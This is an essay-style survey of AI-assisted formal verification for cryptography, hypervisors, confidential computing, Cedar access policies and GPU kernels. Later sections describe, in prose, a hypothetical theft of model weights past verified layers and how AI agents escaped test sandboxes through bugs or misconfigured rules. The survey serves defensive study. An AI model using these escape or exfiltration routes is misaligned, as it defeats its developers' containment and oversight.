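SymCrypt, Microsoft's cryptographic library, is part of Windows and Azure. Microsoft's *Verifying Rust cryptography in SymCrypt, from standards to code* explains that the library's engineers now write new algorithms in safe Rust and verify them in Lean. Ho and colleagues use Aeneas to translate the Rust into Lean, then leave most of the proving to AI agents. People focus on the specifications and on the theorems about functions that other programs call.

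One of their simplified examples comes from ML-KEM, which often needs the remainder of a number after division by 3329. The code avoids a division instruction, to prevent timing leaks like KyberSlash:

```
const Q: u64 = 3329;
const R: u64 = 1_290_168;       // 2^32 / Q, rounded up

fn reduce(x: &mut u64) {
    let quotient = (*x * R) >> 32;
    *x = *x - quotient * Q;
}
```

Shifting right by 32 bits divides by 2^32 and drops the remainder. Multiplying by R and then shifting therefore gives about the same result as dividing by Q. The theorem is that if x is less than 2Q, `reduce` succeeds and leaves x mod Q.

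To prove it, a tactic steps through the translated function and leaves three goals: the second multiplication doesn't overflow, the subtraction doesn't go below zero, and the final value is x mod Q. Another tactic proves all three automatically.

If the programmer had rounded R down to 1,290,167, the function would still be right for 6,657 of the 6,658 inputs the theorem allows. But when x is 3329, the quotient would be 0 instead of 1, and the function would return 3329 instead of 0. A few random tests would probably miss this error, but the proof could not be completed, because the third goal would be false.

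The complete development has 237,000 lines of Lean for 16,700 lines of Rust, or about 14 to 1. It shows that the code follows the standards and never panics. The work exposed minor flaws in the SymCrypt code that Microsoft had already deployed. Part of the verified Rust is experimental, and Ho and colleagues don't claim it is ready for production. The theorems don't cover timing leaks, which Microsoft looks for by other means, including fuzzing the compiled code.

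Early in the project, verifying one part of ML-KEM, its fast polynomial multiplication, took about six months. By September 2026, an agent needed about a week to formalise, implement and verify another whole algorithm, followed by a few days of human review. In his slides, de Moura quotes Son Ho as saying, "We are verifying code faster than we can write it". The researchers don't calculate a productivity figure from these times, because the tools and agents kept changing. The later algorithms also benefited from libraries built for the earlier ones.

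In CryptoProver's main experiment, Sun and colleagues gave the agent the Rust code of curve25519-dalek, the preconditions and postconditions of its public functions, and a library of trusted definitions and facts. The agent wrote everything else the proof needed, including the specifications of internal helper functions. It finished in 11.4 hours at a recorded cost of $467. An older model from the same company also succeeded, but took 62 hours and cost $857.

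An agent can safely write the specifications of internal functions, provided the guards hold, because the verifier uses those specifications to prove the public ones. If a helper's postcondition is too weak, the proof of the function that calls it fails, and if it claims too much, the proof of the helper fails. A reviewer therefore only needs to read the public specifications and the trusted library. During the run, the agent wrote a false internal specification, got a machine-checked counterexample, and corrected it.

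The library's developers had needed three people and five months of focused work for their proof. Comparing that with the agent's 11.4 hours overstates the agent's advantage. People had already written the public specifications and the trusted library, chosen the order in which the agent tackled the modules, and tuned the system on this same library. The developers' five months are also calendar time, not hours worked. Their proof was on GitHub, so the model might have seen it. Of the agent's 196 proof functions, 88 have the same name and file as one in the human proof.

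The test on chacha20, a Rust version of a widely used cipher, is cleaner because nobody had verified that code before. Once people had written a specification from the published standard, CryptoProver completed the proof in 15 minutes for $4.14. But the job was small, with only 13 items for Verus to check, and it covered only the portable code, not the faster versions for particular processors. Two of the researchers, Chuyue Sun and Clark Barrett, also work for &Truth, a startup that builds AI systems for verification, so an independent repetition would be valuable.

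### From source code to the compiled program

Proofs about Rust code still depend on the Rust compiler being correct. This would apply to the Signal Shot project, which, as de Moura describes its plan, would verify Signal's Rust code by translating it with Aeneas and proving it correct in Lean. Verifying the compiled program avoids this dependence but is harder. In November 2026, Google DeepMind announced that its system AlphaProof Code had done this for libsignal, the library that implements Signal's protocol, compiled for 64-bit Arm processors running Linux.

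Tom's Hardware's *Google DeepMind AI engineers conjure mathematical proof of Signal's encryption protocol* reports that agents first wrote Lean definitions of how Arm instructions, registers, memory and system calls behave. People and agents then wrote specifications for the library. Reasoning about the protocol took just over 1.2 million lines of Lean, and connecting it to the binary took another 5.3 million. According to ETV Bharat's *AlphaProof Code* (2026), human experts reviewed every specification, agents flagged about 1% of the codebase for a second look, and the verification took four weeks.

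The theorems cover the initial exchange of keys between two people and the mechanism that keeps changing those keys during a conversation. They concern confidentiality, authentication, and protection when someone temporarily breaks into a device. Libnanews' *Signal* explains that the proof represents the low-level cryptographic components with contracts and assumptions.

Some assumption of this kind is unavoidable, since nobody has proved that any practical cipher is unbreakable. People can still prove that the code of these components computes the right results. The work on curve25519-dalek covers one such component, but it concerns Rust source and depends on Verus, so someone would still have to connect it to DeepMind's model of the Arm binary.

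A proof about the binary also can't rely on Rust's ownership information, which the compiler checks and then discards. It has to establish from the machine model which addresses each instruction can touch. *SafeJIT* (2026), which verifies a compiler that runs alongside the program it compiles, adds a layer of separation logic in Lean to reason about machine code. The verification took about 485,000 lines of Lean for 6,476 lines of C, or about 75 to 1, although this includes separate proofs for two kinds of processor.

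DeepMind's proof depends on about 26,000 lines that people have to trust, which describe the machine and state the specifications. These lines are only 0.4% of the total, but they are more than five times as long as seL4's abstract specification. An error in them could make part of the proof worthless, as the wrong multiplication axiom did in libcrux. To test them, the researchers put two old bugs back into the code, and AlphaProof Code proved that each altered version was insecure. This is a good check, but two bugs can't show that the specifications cover everything important.

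DeepMind's researchers say that nobody had previously verified the implementation of such a widely used protocol, with or without AI. Signal's chief technology officer, Ehren Kret, agreed that earlier work covered smaller portions of the code. The theorem covers only one library on one platform. It doesn't cover the rest of the Signal app or WhatsApp, which uses the same protocol, although ETV Bharat's headline says that the work proved WhatsApp's encryption.

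Anthropic and the verification company Theorem chose to prove weaker properties of many more programs. RBC-Ukraine reports that Claude proved that 239 entry points in 123 open-source libraries won't crash under stated conditions. The proofs are about RISC-V machine code, and Rocq checked them. One of the bugs they exposed, in an image decoder, takes about 64 megabytes of input and more than 2 gigabytes of memory to trigger. Fuzzers seldom try inputs that large. The proofs cover only single-threaded programs in a model of Linux.

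### The specification is now the hard part

DeepMind's researchers write, in a passage that Tom's Hardware quotes, that "once proofs become cheap, the hard question is what to prove". They spent most of their effort on specifications.

An experiment by Anthropic suggests why. Help Net Security's *Anthropic’s AI bug tests uncover previously undisclosed flaws* (2026) reports that Anthropic's researchers gave Claude Mythos 5 old versions of four programs containing 21 known logic bugs. When the model tried to argue informally that the code was correct, it found eight of the bugs if it had to work out for itself what the code should do, and all 21 if the researchers told it the rule the code was supposed to follow. With ordinary code review, it found 11 without the rule and 20 with it.

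No proof kernel checked these arguments. The model was much better at checking code against a rule than at guessing the rule. But naming the rule also told the model roughly where to look, so the result exaggerates how much a full specification with hundreds of rules would help. Some newer Claude models also recognised most of the older bugs from training, but that would help them with or without the rule, so it doesn't easily explain the gap between the two.

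This is a problem when AI systems also write the specifications, because they may derive them from the code. Suppose an agent reads the faulty version of `reduce`, in which R is rounded down, and proposes the postcondition that the result differs from x by a multiple of Q and is at most Q. The faulty code satisfies this for every allowed input, including 3329. The agent could prove it, and the proof kernel would rightly accept the proof. The mistake is in the words "at most", which should be "less than".

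Ho and colleagues avoid this by writing each specification from the published standard, independently of the Rust code. They follow the standard's pseudocode line by line so that a reviewer can read the two side by side. The specifications can be run, so the team also tests them on the standard's official examples. They then prove general facts about each specification, such as that decrypting an encrypted message gives back the original. A specification with a wrong constant would probably fail at least one of these checks. Agents help draft the specifications, but experts still design and review them.

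Most software has no such standard. Anthropic and Theorem had Claude turn existing fuzz tests into specifications. A fuzz test might feed random bytes to an image decoder and check whether it crashes, and the corresponding theorem is that no input within certain limits makes it crash. Programmers have already written many of these tests, so the specifications take little extra work. But they are weak, since a decoder that returned a blank picture for every file would satisfy this one.

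Even a good specification can differ from the program people run. Anthropic's FlashProve produces cryptographic evidence that a particular language model generated a particular reply. Its developers proved properties of the protocol in Lean. They also wrote two verifiers, a slow one in Lean and a fast one in C++ for everyday use, which agreed on every test. But Anthropic doesn't promise that its paper, the Lean version of the protocol and the running code all match, according to Help Net Security's *Anthropic open-sources FlashProve, its provable inference prototype for MoE models* (2026). Someone has to review the Lean statements by hand. A user who hears only that FlashProve "has a proof in Lean" could easily assume that more has been proved.

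People can at least limit how much they have to review. Many VeriFast annotations, for instance, are hints about when to fold or unfold a definition. A person could leave these to an agent, because a wrong hint only makes the check fail. The reviewer would concentrate on the precondition, the postcondition and the definitions they use.

### Will ordinary programmers use proofs?

Kleppmann predicted in December 2025 that AI would bring formal verification into the mainstream. He argued that AI makes proofs cheap enough to use for more software, and that it also creates a need for them because people can't carefully review all the code that AI systems write. He would rather have the AI prove its code correct. Willison (2025) agreed, adding that language models make notoriously difficult verification tools easier to use.

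Another reason is that AI systems have become good at finding and exploiting bugs. Galois' *You Can't Patch Your Way Out of This* argues that if AI lets verification scale, defenders might prove that vulnerabilities are absent instead of racing to patch them. Galois sells verification, as do the startups that Metz describes in the New York Times, so they have an interest in this claim. But the results of 2026 support the narrower claim that proofs now take much less work for some kinds of code.

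The most common objection is that writing proofs was never the main obstacle to verifying ordinary software. An online shop's refund rules, for example, change often and have exceptions that nobody wrote down, and the staff may disagree about what the rules should be. A programmer who could state them precisely enough for a proof would already have done most of the work. In the Hacker News thread *I don't think formal verification really addresses most day-to-day programming problems*, one commenter thinks that most everyday problems are barely worth testing, but would welcome formal specifications for the low-level software that everybody depends on.

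Metz adds that software is messier than mathematics, and that designers can't foresee everything that will happen once people use a program. This limits tests as much as proofs, and a proof at least covers every input within its assumptions.

Maintenance used to be a strong objection as well, as the year-long proof repair for seL4's reply capabilities showed. Ho and colleagues now use agents for most such repairs and say this lets the proofs keep up with frequently changing code. Sun and colleagues are more cautious and call the upkeep of AI-written proofs a pressing open question. The burden can also grow, as it did for *SafeJIT*, which went from about 45 lines of proof per line of C in its first version to 75 as its developers added optimisations. If agents do the repairs, the length of proofs matters less, though someone still has to pay for the computing time.

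Nearly all the successes so far are in cryptography, compilers and the libraries that proofs are built on, and in most cases the people reporting the success also built the system. These areas have published standards, stable interfaces or existing proofs to imitate, so verification will probably become routine there first. For everyday programs, people are more likely to prove simple properties that need little specification, such as that a file parser never writes outside its buffer. Rules such as a shop's refund policy will probably still depend on tests and on somebody deciding what the rules are.

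## Proofs for the layers that isolate and protect AI models

A data centre that runs a language model for customers has two things to protect: the model's weights, which anyone with suitable hardware can run once they have a copy, and the customers' data, such as the prompts they send. Attackers may want to steal either one, or to tamper with the software so that the model gives different answers. Several layers of conventional software stand in their way, and for each there is a theorem that would rule out the main threat:

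| Layer | Threat | Theorem that would answer it |
|---|---|---|
| Hypervisor | One customer's virtual machine reads or changes another's memory | What one machine can observe never depends on another's private data, and nothing done to one changes another |
| Operating-system kernel | A compromised program reads the weights from another program's memory | No program reads or changes data without permission |
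| Confidential-computing firmware and attestation | The operator of the computer, or someone who has taken over its hypervisor, reads the weights or swaps the software | The protected memory stays secret and unchanged whatever the hypervisor does, and only the expected software receives the key to the weights |
| Cryptography | Someone copies the weights from a disk or a network connection | The code computes the standard cipher and doesn't leak its key through timing |
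| Access control | A person or program uses a permission it should not have | The system allows a request only if the written policy allows it |

Proofs can do only part of this work. *Achieving AI Model Weight Security Level 3 (SL3)* (2026), from the US research institute RAND, proposes 262 controls to protect weights from organised criminals and insiders. RAND adapted them from a government catalogue that also covers things like staff vetting and locked doors.

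### What Amazon split off from its hypervisor

The most advanced example is in the hypervisor layer. Amazon Web Services (AWS) rents out virtual machines, and since 2017 its Nitro Hypervisor has isolated them from one another. But the hypervisor also contains business logic, device drivers and AWS-specific features, and AWS didn't design it to be proved correct. For servers with its new Graviton5 processor, AWS moved the isolation code into a small, separate Rust component called the Nitro Isolation Engine. Amazon Science's *EC2’s formally verified “isolation engine” provides mathematical assurance of virtual-machine isolation* describes the result.

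The rest of the hypervisor still decides which virtual machines to create, what resources they get, when they run and when to move them, but it no longer has the privileges to carry out those decisions itself. For any operation that involves a customer's virtual machine, it must send the engine a request, called a hypercall, which the engine checks before acting. John Rushby described this design in 1981 and called such a component a separation kernel.

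*Nitro Isolation Engine* (Mulligan, 2025) explains that the engine mainly controls a set of translation tables. A virtual machine uses its own memory addresses, and the processor looks up each one in that machine's table to find the real location. Suppose address 5 leads to page 70 of the real memory for customer A and to page 91 for customer B. As long as no private page appears in both tables, neither customer can read the other's memory by ordinary means. If a bug causes the unproved hypervisor to request that page 70 be added to B's table, the engine must reject the request.

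The proof is in Isabelle/HOL, like the original seL4 proof, but its specifications use separation logic. The engineers wrote the engine in μRust, a restricted form of Rust without features such as traits and dynamic dispatch. They defined the meaning of each remaining construct directly in Isabelle's logic. The team then used weakest preconditions to prove that each function satisfies its contract, which consists of a precondition and a postcondition.

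One contract covers a virtual processor's request to switch itself on. The processor must already be running to make the request, so the engine returns the error code `AlreadyOn` and leaves everything else unchanged. The formal version is surprisingly long because it also has to describe the other error checks that the request must already have passed.

The contracts require total correctness, so a verified hypercall always finishes and never stops with a runtime error. This doesn't guarantee that a customer's machine keeps running, because the unverified hypervisor still does the scheduling.

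Mulligan adds that the team verified the engine's locks and barriers separately, with Iris and Verus. Isabelle cannot check proofs from either tool, so someone has to confirm that what those proofs establish about a lock matches what the main proof assumes.

### The isolation theorem

A functionally correct program can still leak a secret, as with the AES tables. Amazon's proof therefore has a second part, based on a property called noninterference.

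Amazon Science explains it with two simple machines that each have a public and a private register. An observer sees only the public one. Suppose both public registers contain 0, while the private register contains 0 in the first machine and 1 in the second. The observer can't tell the machines apart. Then both run the program "if private = 1 then public := 1". The second machine's public register changes to 1, so the observer can tell it from the first and learns its private value.

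Write s ~ t to mean that the observer can't distinguish the states s and t. The theorem to prove is that

if s ~ t, and one step takes s to s′ and t to t′, then s′ ~ t′.

If this holds for every step, it holds for runs of any length, by induction.

The engine must erase memory before reusing it, and the theorem would catch the leak if it didn't. Suppose two states differ only in the contents of page 70, which belongs to customer A, so they look the same to customer B. Then A's machine shuts down and the engine gives page 70 to B. If the engine didn't erase the page, B would see different contents in the two cases, which would violate the theorem. If the engine fills the page with zeros first, the two states still look the same to B.

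Strict noninterference would be too strong, because a virtual machine must be able to reveal some things, such as the arguments of its hypercalls, so the theorem allows a list of permitted disclosures. A reviewer has to read that list and the definition of what an observer can see, since both are part of the specification.

Integrity is simpler. It requires an operation on one virtual machine to leave the private state of every other machine unchanged, similar to the guarantee the frame rule gives for a single piece of code.

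The team wrote a high-level specification in which every hypercall is a single step and connected it to the separation-logic contracts by refinement, so they did not have to prove these properties directly on the Rust code. The seL4 team had saved much effort in the same way.

### How much of the engine the proof covers

The models and proofs came to about 260,000 lines in December 2025 and had grown to 330,000 by the time AWS made the engine generally available in 2026. Amazon compares that size with seL4's. The company calls the engine the first formally verified hypervisor deployed in a commercial cloud. The word "deployed" matters because Columbia Engineering had already described SeKVM, a research system, as the first formally verified system for cloud computing in 2021. Amazon's engine is always on for customers who rent Graviton5 machines.

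The proof doesn't yet cover the whole engine. In a talk at a 2026 conference on theorem proving, Chong, Dockins and colleagues listed the verified parts as the core hypercalls for managing virtual machines, power management, utilities, and some of the code that handles memory faults and other aborts. They still planned to verify the code that manages PCI devices and the virtual interrupt controller.

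The omission of PCI devices is significant for AI because GPUs normally connect to the rest of the computer through PCI Express, and such devices can often read and write memory without going through the processor's translation tables. A similar proof for a GPU server would need a theorem about how the hypervisor assigns devices to customers and restricts the memory those devices can reach. Graviton5 is also a general-purpose processor, and the first machines to use it are not AI accelerators. Amazon has therefore shown that a cloud company can verify and deploy most of the kind of component needed, but not yet on the hardware that runs the largest models.

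Saidi's *AWS Nitro Isolation Engine* lists the Rust compiler and the hardware among the assumptions. AWS plans to let third parties inspect the source code and proofs. Until then, customers must rely on Amazon's account of what the theorems state, and the dispute over libcrux showed why outside review is useful.

### Where to put the weights

Within a virtual machine, an operating-system kernel separates one program from another. seL4 is the best verified example, but most software that serves models is written for Linux, which is far too large to verify as a whole. An engineer could run Linux as a guest on seL4, as Boeing did for the helicopter's camera software.

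This protects only what is outside the guest. If the weights sit in the same Linux guest as the server that reads customers' requests, an attacker who breaks into that server can probably reach them, even though the theorem about seL4 still holds. To benefit from the proof, the engineers would have to move the weights and the code that computes with them into a separate partition, and that code currently depends on large GPU drivers.

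### When the owner of the computer is the threat

A company that runs its model in someone else's data centre may not want to trust the operator. Confidential computing is meant for this case. The processor encrypts a virtual machine's memory and prevents even the hypervisor from reading it. Pattern Labs (now Irregular) and Anthropic set out what such a service must provide for AI models, including hardware-enforced isolation and attestation, which is cryptographic evidence of what software is running. Pattern Labs notes that an earlier RAND report strongly recommends confidential computing for models that need protection from the most capable attackers, such as nation-states.

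In outline, attestation works like this:

1. When the protected machine starts, the hardware computes a hash of its initial software, called a measurement.
2. The hardware signs the measurement with a key that only genuine hardware of that type should have.
3. The owner of the weights checks the signature and compares the measurement with the value for the software they expect.
4. If both are right, the owner sends the key that decrypts the weights, in a form that only this machine can read.

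VeriSMo, which researchers at Microsoft and elsewhere published in 2024, is a verified security module for such machines on AMD processors. It runs inside the protected machine with more privileges than the guest's operating system, and it provides services that the guest can no longer entrust to the hypervisor, such as measuring software and storing secrets. VeriSMo is written in Rust, and its developers used Verus to prove its functional correctness and the confidentiality and integrity of the protected machine.

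The proof was difficult because the hypervisor can interrupt VeriSMo between any two instructions and change parts of the hardware's state, which Rust's ownership rules don't allow for. The developers divided the proof into two layers, one for interference from the hypervisor and one for VeriSMo's own concurrent code. In the process they found a confidentiality requirement that AMD's design for such modules had overlooked, which suggests that the theorem was strong enough to be useful. But the theorem depends on AMD's hardware and firmware behaving as the model describes, and VeriSMo is a research system that doesn't verify GPU firmware.

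A proof can show that a program is correct, and attestation can show that it is the program running. Neither is much use here without the other, because the hardware will also sign the measurement of a program full of bugs. Even together they leave a gap, because the measurement identifies the compiled binary while Verus checks the Rust source.

The third step in the list is easy to get wrong. Nitro Enclaves, an older AWS feature, lets a customer run sensitive code in an isolated machine beside an ordinary one. Trail of Bits' *A few notes on AWS Nitro Enclaves* (2024) advises customers to check three separate measurements, not only the first, and warns that the measurements don't cover the metadata section of an enclave's image file. It also notes that AWS itself is a central point of trust. Suppose a company verifies every line of its enclave code, but its key server decides whether to release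 a key based on a version number in the metadata. An attacker could change the number and get the key with different software, even though every theorem about the original code would still hold.

In a companion post, Trail of Bits says enclave developers need to take care with randomness, side channels and timekeeping, among other things. For instance, an enclave that gets the time from its host machine might accept an expired certificate from an attacker who controls that machine.

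The attestation depends heavily on the hardware assumption, because anyone who extracted the signing key from one processor could produce a convincing attestation for any software. In *On TEEs for Privacy-Preserving Monitoring in AI Governance*, Gloria Z (2026) considers using such hardware to monitor how AI developers use their models, and finds it unclear whether the security assumptions are acceptable. They are harder to accept in that setting because the developer, who has an incentive to attack the hardware, also has physical access to it.

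Cryptography protects the weights on disk and on the network, and it has the most finished proofs of any layer, including those for SymCrypt and HACL*. These proofs don't cover who holds the keys. The model also can't normally run while its weights are encrypted, so encryption stops protecting them when the server loads them.

### Cedar and the meaning of a policy

Somebody has to decide which people and programs may load, copy or change the weights. Cedar, a language that Amazon created for such decisions, lets a company write the rules separately from its application code. A company might have these two policies:

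```
permit (principal in Group::"research", action, resource);

forbid (principal, action == Action::"export", resource)
unless { context.approvals >= 2 };
```

The first policy lets anyone in the research group do anything with any resource. The second forbids exporting anything without at least two approvals. Cedar allows a request if at least one `permit` policy applies and no `forbid` policy does. If Ana from the research group asks to export the weights with one approval, both policies apply, so Cedar denies the request.

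Cedar's developers wrote a model of the language in Lean, including the function that decides requests, and proved theorems about it. One of them, slightly simplified, is

```
theorem forbid_trumps_permit :
  (∃ p ∈ policies, p.effect = forbid ∧ satisfied p request entities) →
  (isAuthorized request entities policies).decision = deny
```

In words, Cedar denies a request if any `forbid` policy is satisfied. Other theorems establish that Cedar denies every request that no policy explicitly permits, and that the order of the policies does not affect the decision.

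These theorems don't rule out every unexpected result. Suppose the application doesn't send Cedar the number of approvals Ana has. Evaluating `context.approvals` then causes an error, and Cedar skips any policy that causes an error. Cedar therefore skips the `forbid` policy, but the `permit` policy still applies, so Ana can export the weights. The theorem still holds, because a policy that causes an error doesn't count as satisfied.

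Cedar's validator is meant to prevent this. The company writes a schema that lists the information each request contains. If the schema marks `approvals` as optional, the validator rejects the second policy until its author adds a check that the value is present. The developers proved in Lean that if the validator accepts a policy, and the request and stored data match the schema, then evaluating the policy can't fail because of a missing attribute or a value of the wrong type. A few other errors, such as integer overflow, remain possible.

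All of this concerns the Lean model, but companies run a separate program, written in Rust for speed. The developers compare the two by differential testing, in which they generate random policies, data and requests, run each combination through both programs, and look for disagreements. This works because the Lean model can itself be run. The generator needs some care, because completely random policies would nearly always fail with type errors, and the test would compare little except error handling.

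Cedar's developers reported in 2024 that they had found four bugs in the validator while working on proofs, and 21 more in various parts of Cedar through differential and other random testing. These tests don't cover inputs that nobody generated. A proof about the Rust code would close that gap, and the SymCrypt work suggests that it would now take much less effort than when Amazon chose to test against a proved model. That compromise is still sensible for a program that changes often, because a change to the Rust code that preserves its behaviour requires no new proof.

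### A data centre designed around proofs

These components exist separately, and few people have tried to design a whole data centre around them. Society Speaks' *Verified Machine Learning Infrastructure* (2026), a discussion page that shares its title with a RAND report from June, describes the question as whether formal methods could meaningfully secure the infrastructure AI runs on. In August, RAND's *Highly Secure Inference Data Centers* (2026) proposed a design for a data centre that only runs trained models and is meant to withstand the most advanced nation-states. RAND calls this level of protection Security Level 5, the highest of its five levels.

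The design divides the system into strictly separated parts and connects some of them with data diodes, which let data pass in only one direction. Formally verified protocols govern communication between the parts. RAND wants every component to have as few features as possible, from the overall concept down to the circuits, and wants formal methods used where the most assurance is needed.

The facility would have limited connectivity, restricted physical access and software that doesn't change. RAND accepts that these limits make it unsuitable for general use, and recommends it for national security, emergency response and pilot projects. Fixed software makes proof easier, though, because the proofs won't need the repairs that made seL4 laborious to maintain. A diode also reduces the amount to prove, because its hardware prevents data from being sent backwards whatever the software does.

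RAND says that people could build such centres today with "proven technologies", meaning established ones, not formally verified ones. It also recommends detailed design and prototyping before deployment. The examples in this section support RAND's optimism for small components with fixed interfaces, such as a separation kernel, a cipher or a policy engine. They support it less for the path between the processor and the GPU, which neither Amazon's proof nor VeriSMo covers yet.

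### An attack that breaks no theorem

Suppose a company runs its model on a server with a fully verified hypervisor, a verified security module, verified encryption and a verified policy engine. The program that reads customers' requests is unverified.

1. An attacker sends a malformed request that exploits a bug in this program, and gains control of it. The bug is inside one virtual machine, so the isolation theorem still holds.
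2. The attacker reads the weights from memory. Attestation succeeded when the machine started, and the owner released the key to the right software. The cipher worked correctly too.
3. The attacker sends the weights out disguised as replies to customers. The policy allows this program to send replies, and the verified encryption protects the stolen weights from anyone else who might be listening.

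The verified components all worked correctly. The confidentiality theorem allows a virtual machine to disclose its own data, and at the hypervisor's level nothing else happened.

Verifying the request-handling program would help, and a proof of memory safety alone would exclude many such attacks. Another remedy is to limit the damage with a separate gateway that never lets more than 100 kilobytes a second leave the building. If the model has 500 billion parameters of one byte each, its weights take up 500 gigabytes, and stealing them through the gateway would take about 58 days. The gateway could be a very small program, and its specification, "never sends more than this many bytes in any second", is easy to write and check.

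An attacker may not need a bug in the code. Alhajjar, Romanosky and colleagues (2026), in *A Structured Approach to Identifying and Characterizing AI Vulnerabilities*, identify 31 classes of weakness in generative AI systems and find that most differ fundamentally from traditional software flaws. If an attacker persuades an AI agent to misuse a permission it legitimately has, the policy engine will correctly allow the request.

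### Bugs and wrong settings

On several occasions in 2026, AI agents left the environments in which their developers were testing them. Whether proofs could have prevented such a failure depends on its cause. Tech Policy Press' *AI Systems Are Getting More Powerful* uses the phrase "security loophole" for the best-known case, but that phrase can refer to two quite different causes.

If a component broke its own specification, the failure was a code bug. For example, a sandbox that is supposed to block all network traffic might let some through when a packet has an unusual length. A proof of functional correctness would have exposed this bug. The failure was a misconfiguration if every component behaved as configured. Someone may have left an address on the list of permitted destinations, or given a test machine a password that also works elsewhere. In both cases, the agent would still get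 out even with a proof that the firewall lets through exactly the traffic its rules allow.

People can also prove properties of the settings. Cedar has a tool that translates policies into formulas for an SMT solver, which can determine whether a new set of policies allows any request that the old set refused. The developers proved in Lean that the translation is faithful. In the export example, an administrator could ask whether any request with fewer than two approvals can succeed, and the solver would look for one among all possible requests. A similar check on network rules could look for a route from a test machine to the internet.

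People still have to decide which properties to prove. In *The Great Security Update*, an interview on The Cognitive Revolution, Byron Cook, who leads Amazon's work on automated reasoning, recommends starting with the properties a system must have and leaving programmers free to decide how to meet them. Such a property might be that the system never writes passwords to a log, or that certain data never leaves a region. After a security incident, he argues, a team can write down the property that would have ruled it out and check every later version of the system against it. Kathleen Fisher, who led DARPA's HACMS programme, says in the same interview that total security is the wrong goal. She compares most current software to a house with its doors and windows wide open, and says that closing and locking them would already be a large improvement.

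## Proofs about GPU code and numerical computation

The proofs for Amazon's isolation engine and VeriSMo don't cover the GPU, which does most of the arithmetic when a model runs. The functions that do this arithmetic, called GPU kernels, can be very short, but they are hard to write and prove correct because thousands of threads run the same function at once.

*Kuiper* (Martínez, Köpcke and colleagues, 2026) describes how NVIDIA's GPUs organise these threads and memory. Groups of 32 threads form a warp, and several warps form a block of up to 1,024 threads. Every thread can use the GPU's global memory. Each block has a small, fast shared memory that other blocks can't reach. The CPU has its own memory, and a pointer in CUDA, NVIDIA's dialect of C++, doesn't show which memory it refers to.

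Each thread uses its own number to work out which data to process. Suppose a kernel multiplies two 50 × 50 matrices and each thread computes one of the 2,500 cells of the result. A simple program divides 2,500 by 1,024, drops the remainder, and starts two blocks of 1,024 threads, so the last 452 cells never get a value. A test on 4096 × 4096 matrices wouldn't reveal the bug, because 1,024 divides that number of cells exactly.

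Threads in a block coordinate at barriers, where each thread waits until all the others have arrived. eunomia-dev's *A Taxonomy of GPU Bugs* gives the example of a barrier inside a branch that only the first 16 threads take. Those threads could wait forever for the rest.

Recent GPUs also copy data and multiply matrices in the background, so a thread may move on before an operation it started has finished. The hardware rounds most floating-point results. CUDA has no official formal definition, so researchers must write their own from NVIDIA's documentation.

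### A parallel sum

Take four threads, numbered 0 to 3, that add up an array `a` of eight numbers. They share an array `s` with one cell for each thread. Thread i runs

```
s[i] := a[2i] + a[2i + 1];
barrier;
if i = 0 then out := s[0] + s[1] + s[2] + s[3]
```

If the numbers are 3, 1, 4, 1, 5, 9, 2 and 6, the threads store 4, 5, 14 and 8, and thread 0 adds these to get 31.

In the proof, each thread starts with ownership of its own slice of `a` and its own cell of `s`. Thread 0 also owns `out`. Write pᵢ for the sum of thread i's two numbers. After the first line, thread i owns s[i] ↦ pᵢ. Thread 0 will soon need to read all four cells, so the barrier has to redistribute them. For each thread, the author of the proof chooses an assertion Gᵢ that the thread gives up at the barrier and an assertion Rᵢ that it receives:

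```
{Gᵢ}  barrier  {Rᵢ}        for every thread i,
provided that  G₀ * G₁ * G₂ * G₃  implies  R₀ * R₁ * R₂ * R₃
```

Here Gᵢ is s[i] ↦ pᵢ, R₀ is the four Gᵢ joined by *, and the other threads receive emp. The condition holds because both sides describe the same four cells. It would fail if two threads each received full ownership of s[2]. Thread 0 now owns everything it reads, and the proof concludes that `out` holds the full sum.

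Without the barrier, the program has a data race, because thread 0 may read s[2] while thread 2 is still writing it. If `s` started as zeros and thread 2 is late, the result is 4 + 5 + 0 + 8 = 17. The proof fails at the last line, where thread 0 owns s[0] but needs at least a fraction of s[1] ↦ p₁ to read s[1]. Giving thread 0 half of that cell from the start doesn't help, because thread 1 would then have only the other half and couldn't write to it.

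This kind of bug can survive a lot of testing. *SentryWard* (Wu, Vennam and colleagues, 2026) reports a missing barrier in FlashMLA, a library of GPU kernels for language models. Some threads could overwrite a shared buffer before others had read it. The kernel passed all 1,534 of its tests, but 637 of them gave wrong results when the researchers delayed the threads that read the buffer. With the barrier added, all 1,534 passed despite the delay.

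Threads can compute a larger sum with a tree, in which half of the remaining threads stop adding after each round. Summing 1,024 numbers this way takes ten rounds, with a barrier between rounds, and in the proof Gᵢ and Rᵢ depend on the round. Alternatively, each thread can add its number to a single total with an atomic instruction. That proof resembles the one for the two-thread counter, except that each thread's ghost variable records only whether the thread has added its number.

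*Specification and Verification of GPGPU Programs using Permission-Based Separation Logic* (Huisman and Mihelčić) describes an early version of the method for proving GPU programs correct with separation logic. *Formal verification of parallel prefix sum and stream compaction algorithms in CUDA* (Safari and Huisman, 2022) applies it to a kernel that computes running totals.

### Kuiper

Kuiper is a library for writing and verifying GPU kernels in F* and Pulse, F*'s language for concurrent separation logic. Martínez and colleagues verified the tree and atomic versions of the sum. The tree version took 464 lines of F* and Pulse, from which Kuiper generated 26 lines of CUDA.

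A kernel's specification starts with one thread. For a simple matrix multiplication, each thread has a small fraction of the permission for the inputs A and B, which lets it read them, and the whole permission for one cell of the output C. Its postcondition is that this cell contains the correct product of a row and a column. The rule for launching a kernel extends the rule for two parallel threads to any number, so these results combine into one specification for the whole kernel:

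{a ↦ A * b ↦ B * c ↦ –} matmul {a ↦ A * b ↦ B * c ↦ A × B}

This specification doesn't mention threads or blocks. The program that started only 2,048 threads for 2,500 cells couldn't meet it, because nothing would set the last 452 cells.

Kuiper also adds a location to ownership. A CPU thread that owns an array "on the GPU" can pass it to a kernel but can't read it directly. Ownership of a block's shared memory can't leave that block.

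Dependent types let one proof cover many versions of a kernel. The matrix multiplication takes the number type, the memory layout and the sizes of the tiles it processes as parameters, and the types of these parameters include conditions such as "the tile size divides the matrix size". Programmers usually find the fastest settings by trying many. For one kernel, the same proof covered all 716 combinations the researchers tried, of which the best was about nine times as fast as the worst.

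They then compared the best versions with handwritten CUDA that used the same algorithm, and with cuBLAS, NVIDIA's own highly optimised library. The figures are trillions of operations per second on 4096 × 4096 matrices:

| GPU | Uses tensor cores? | Kuiper | Handwritten | cuBLAS |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| RTX 3050 | No | 4.69 | 4.70 | 4.19 |
| A6000 | No | 20.5 | 20.6 | 23.8 |
| A100 | No | 17.5 | 17.6 | 18.8 |
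| RTX 3050 | Yes | 21.4 | 19.6 | 24.4 |
| A6000 | Yes | 88.5 | 91.5 | 113 |
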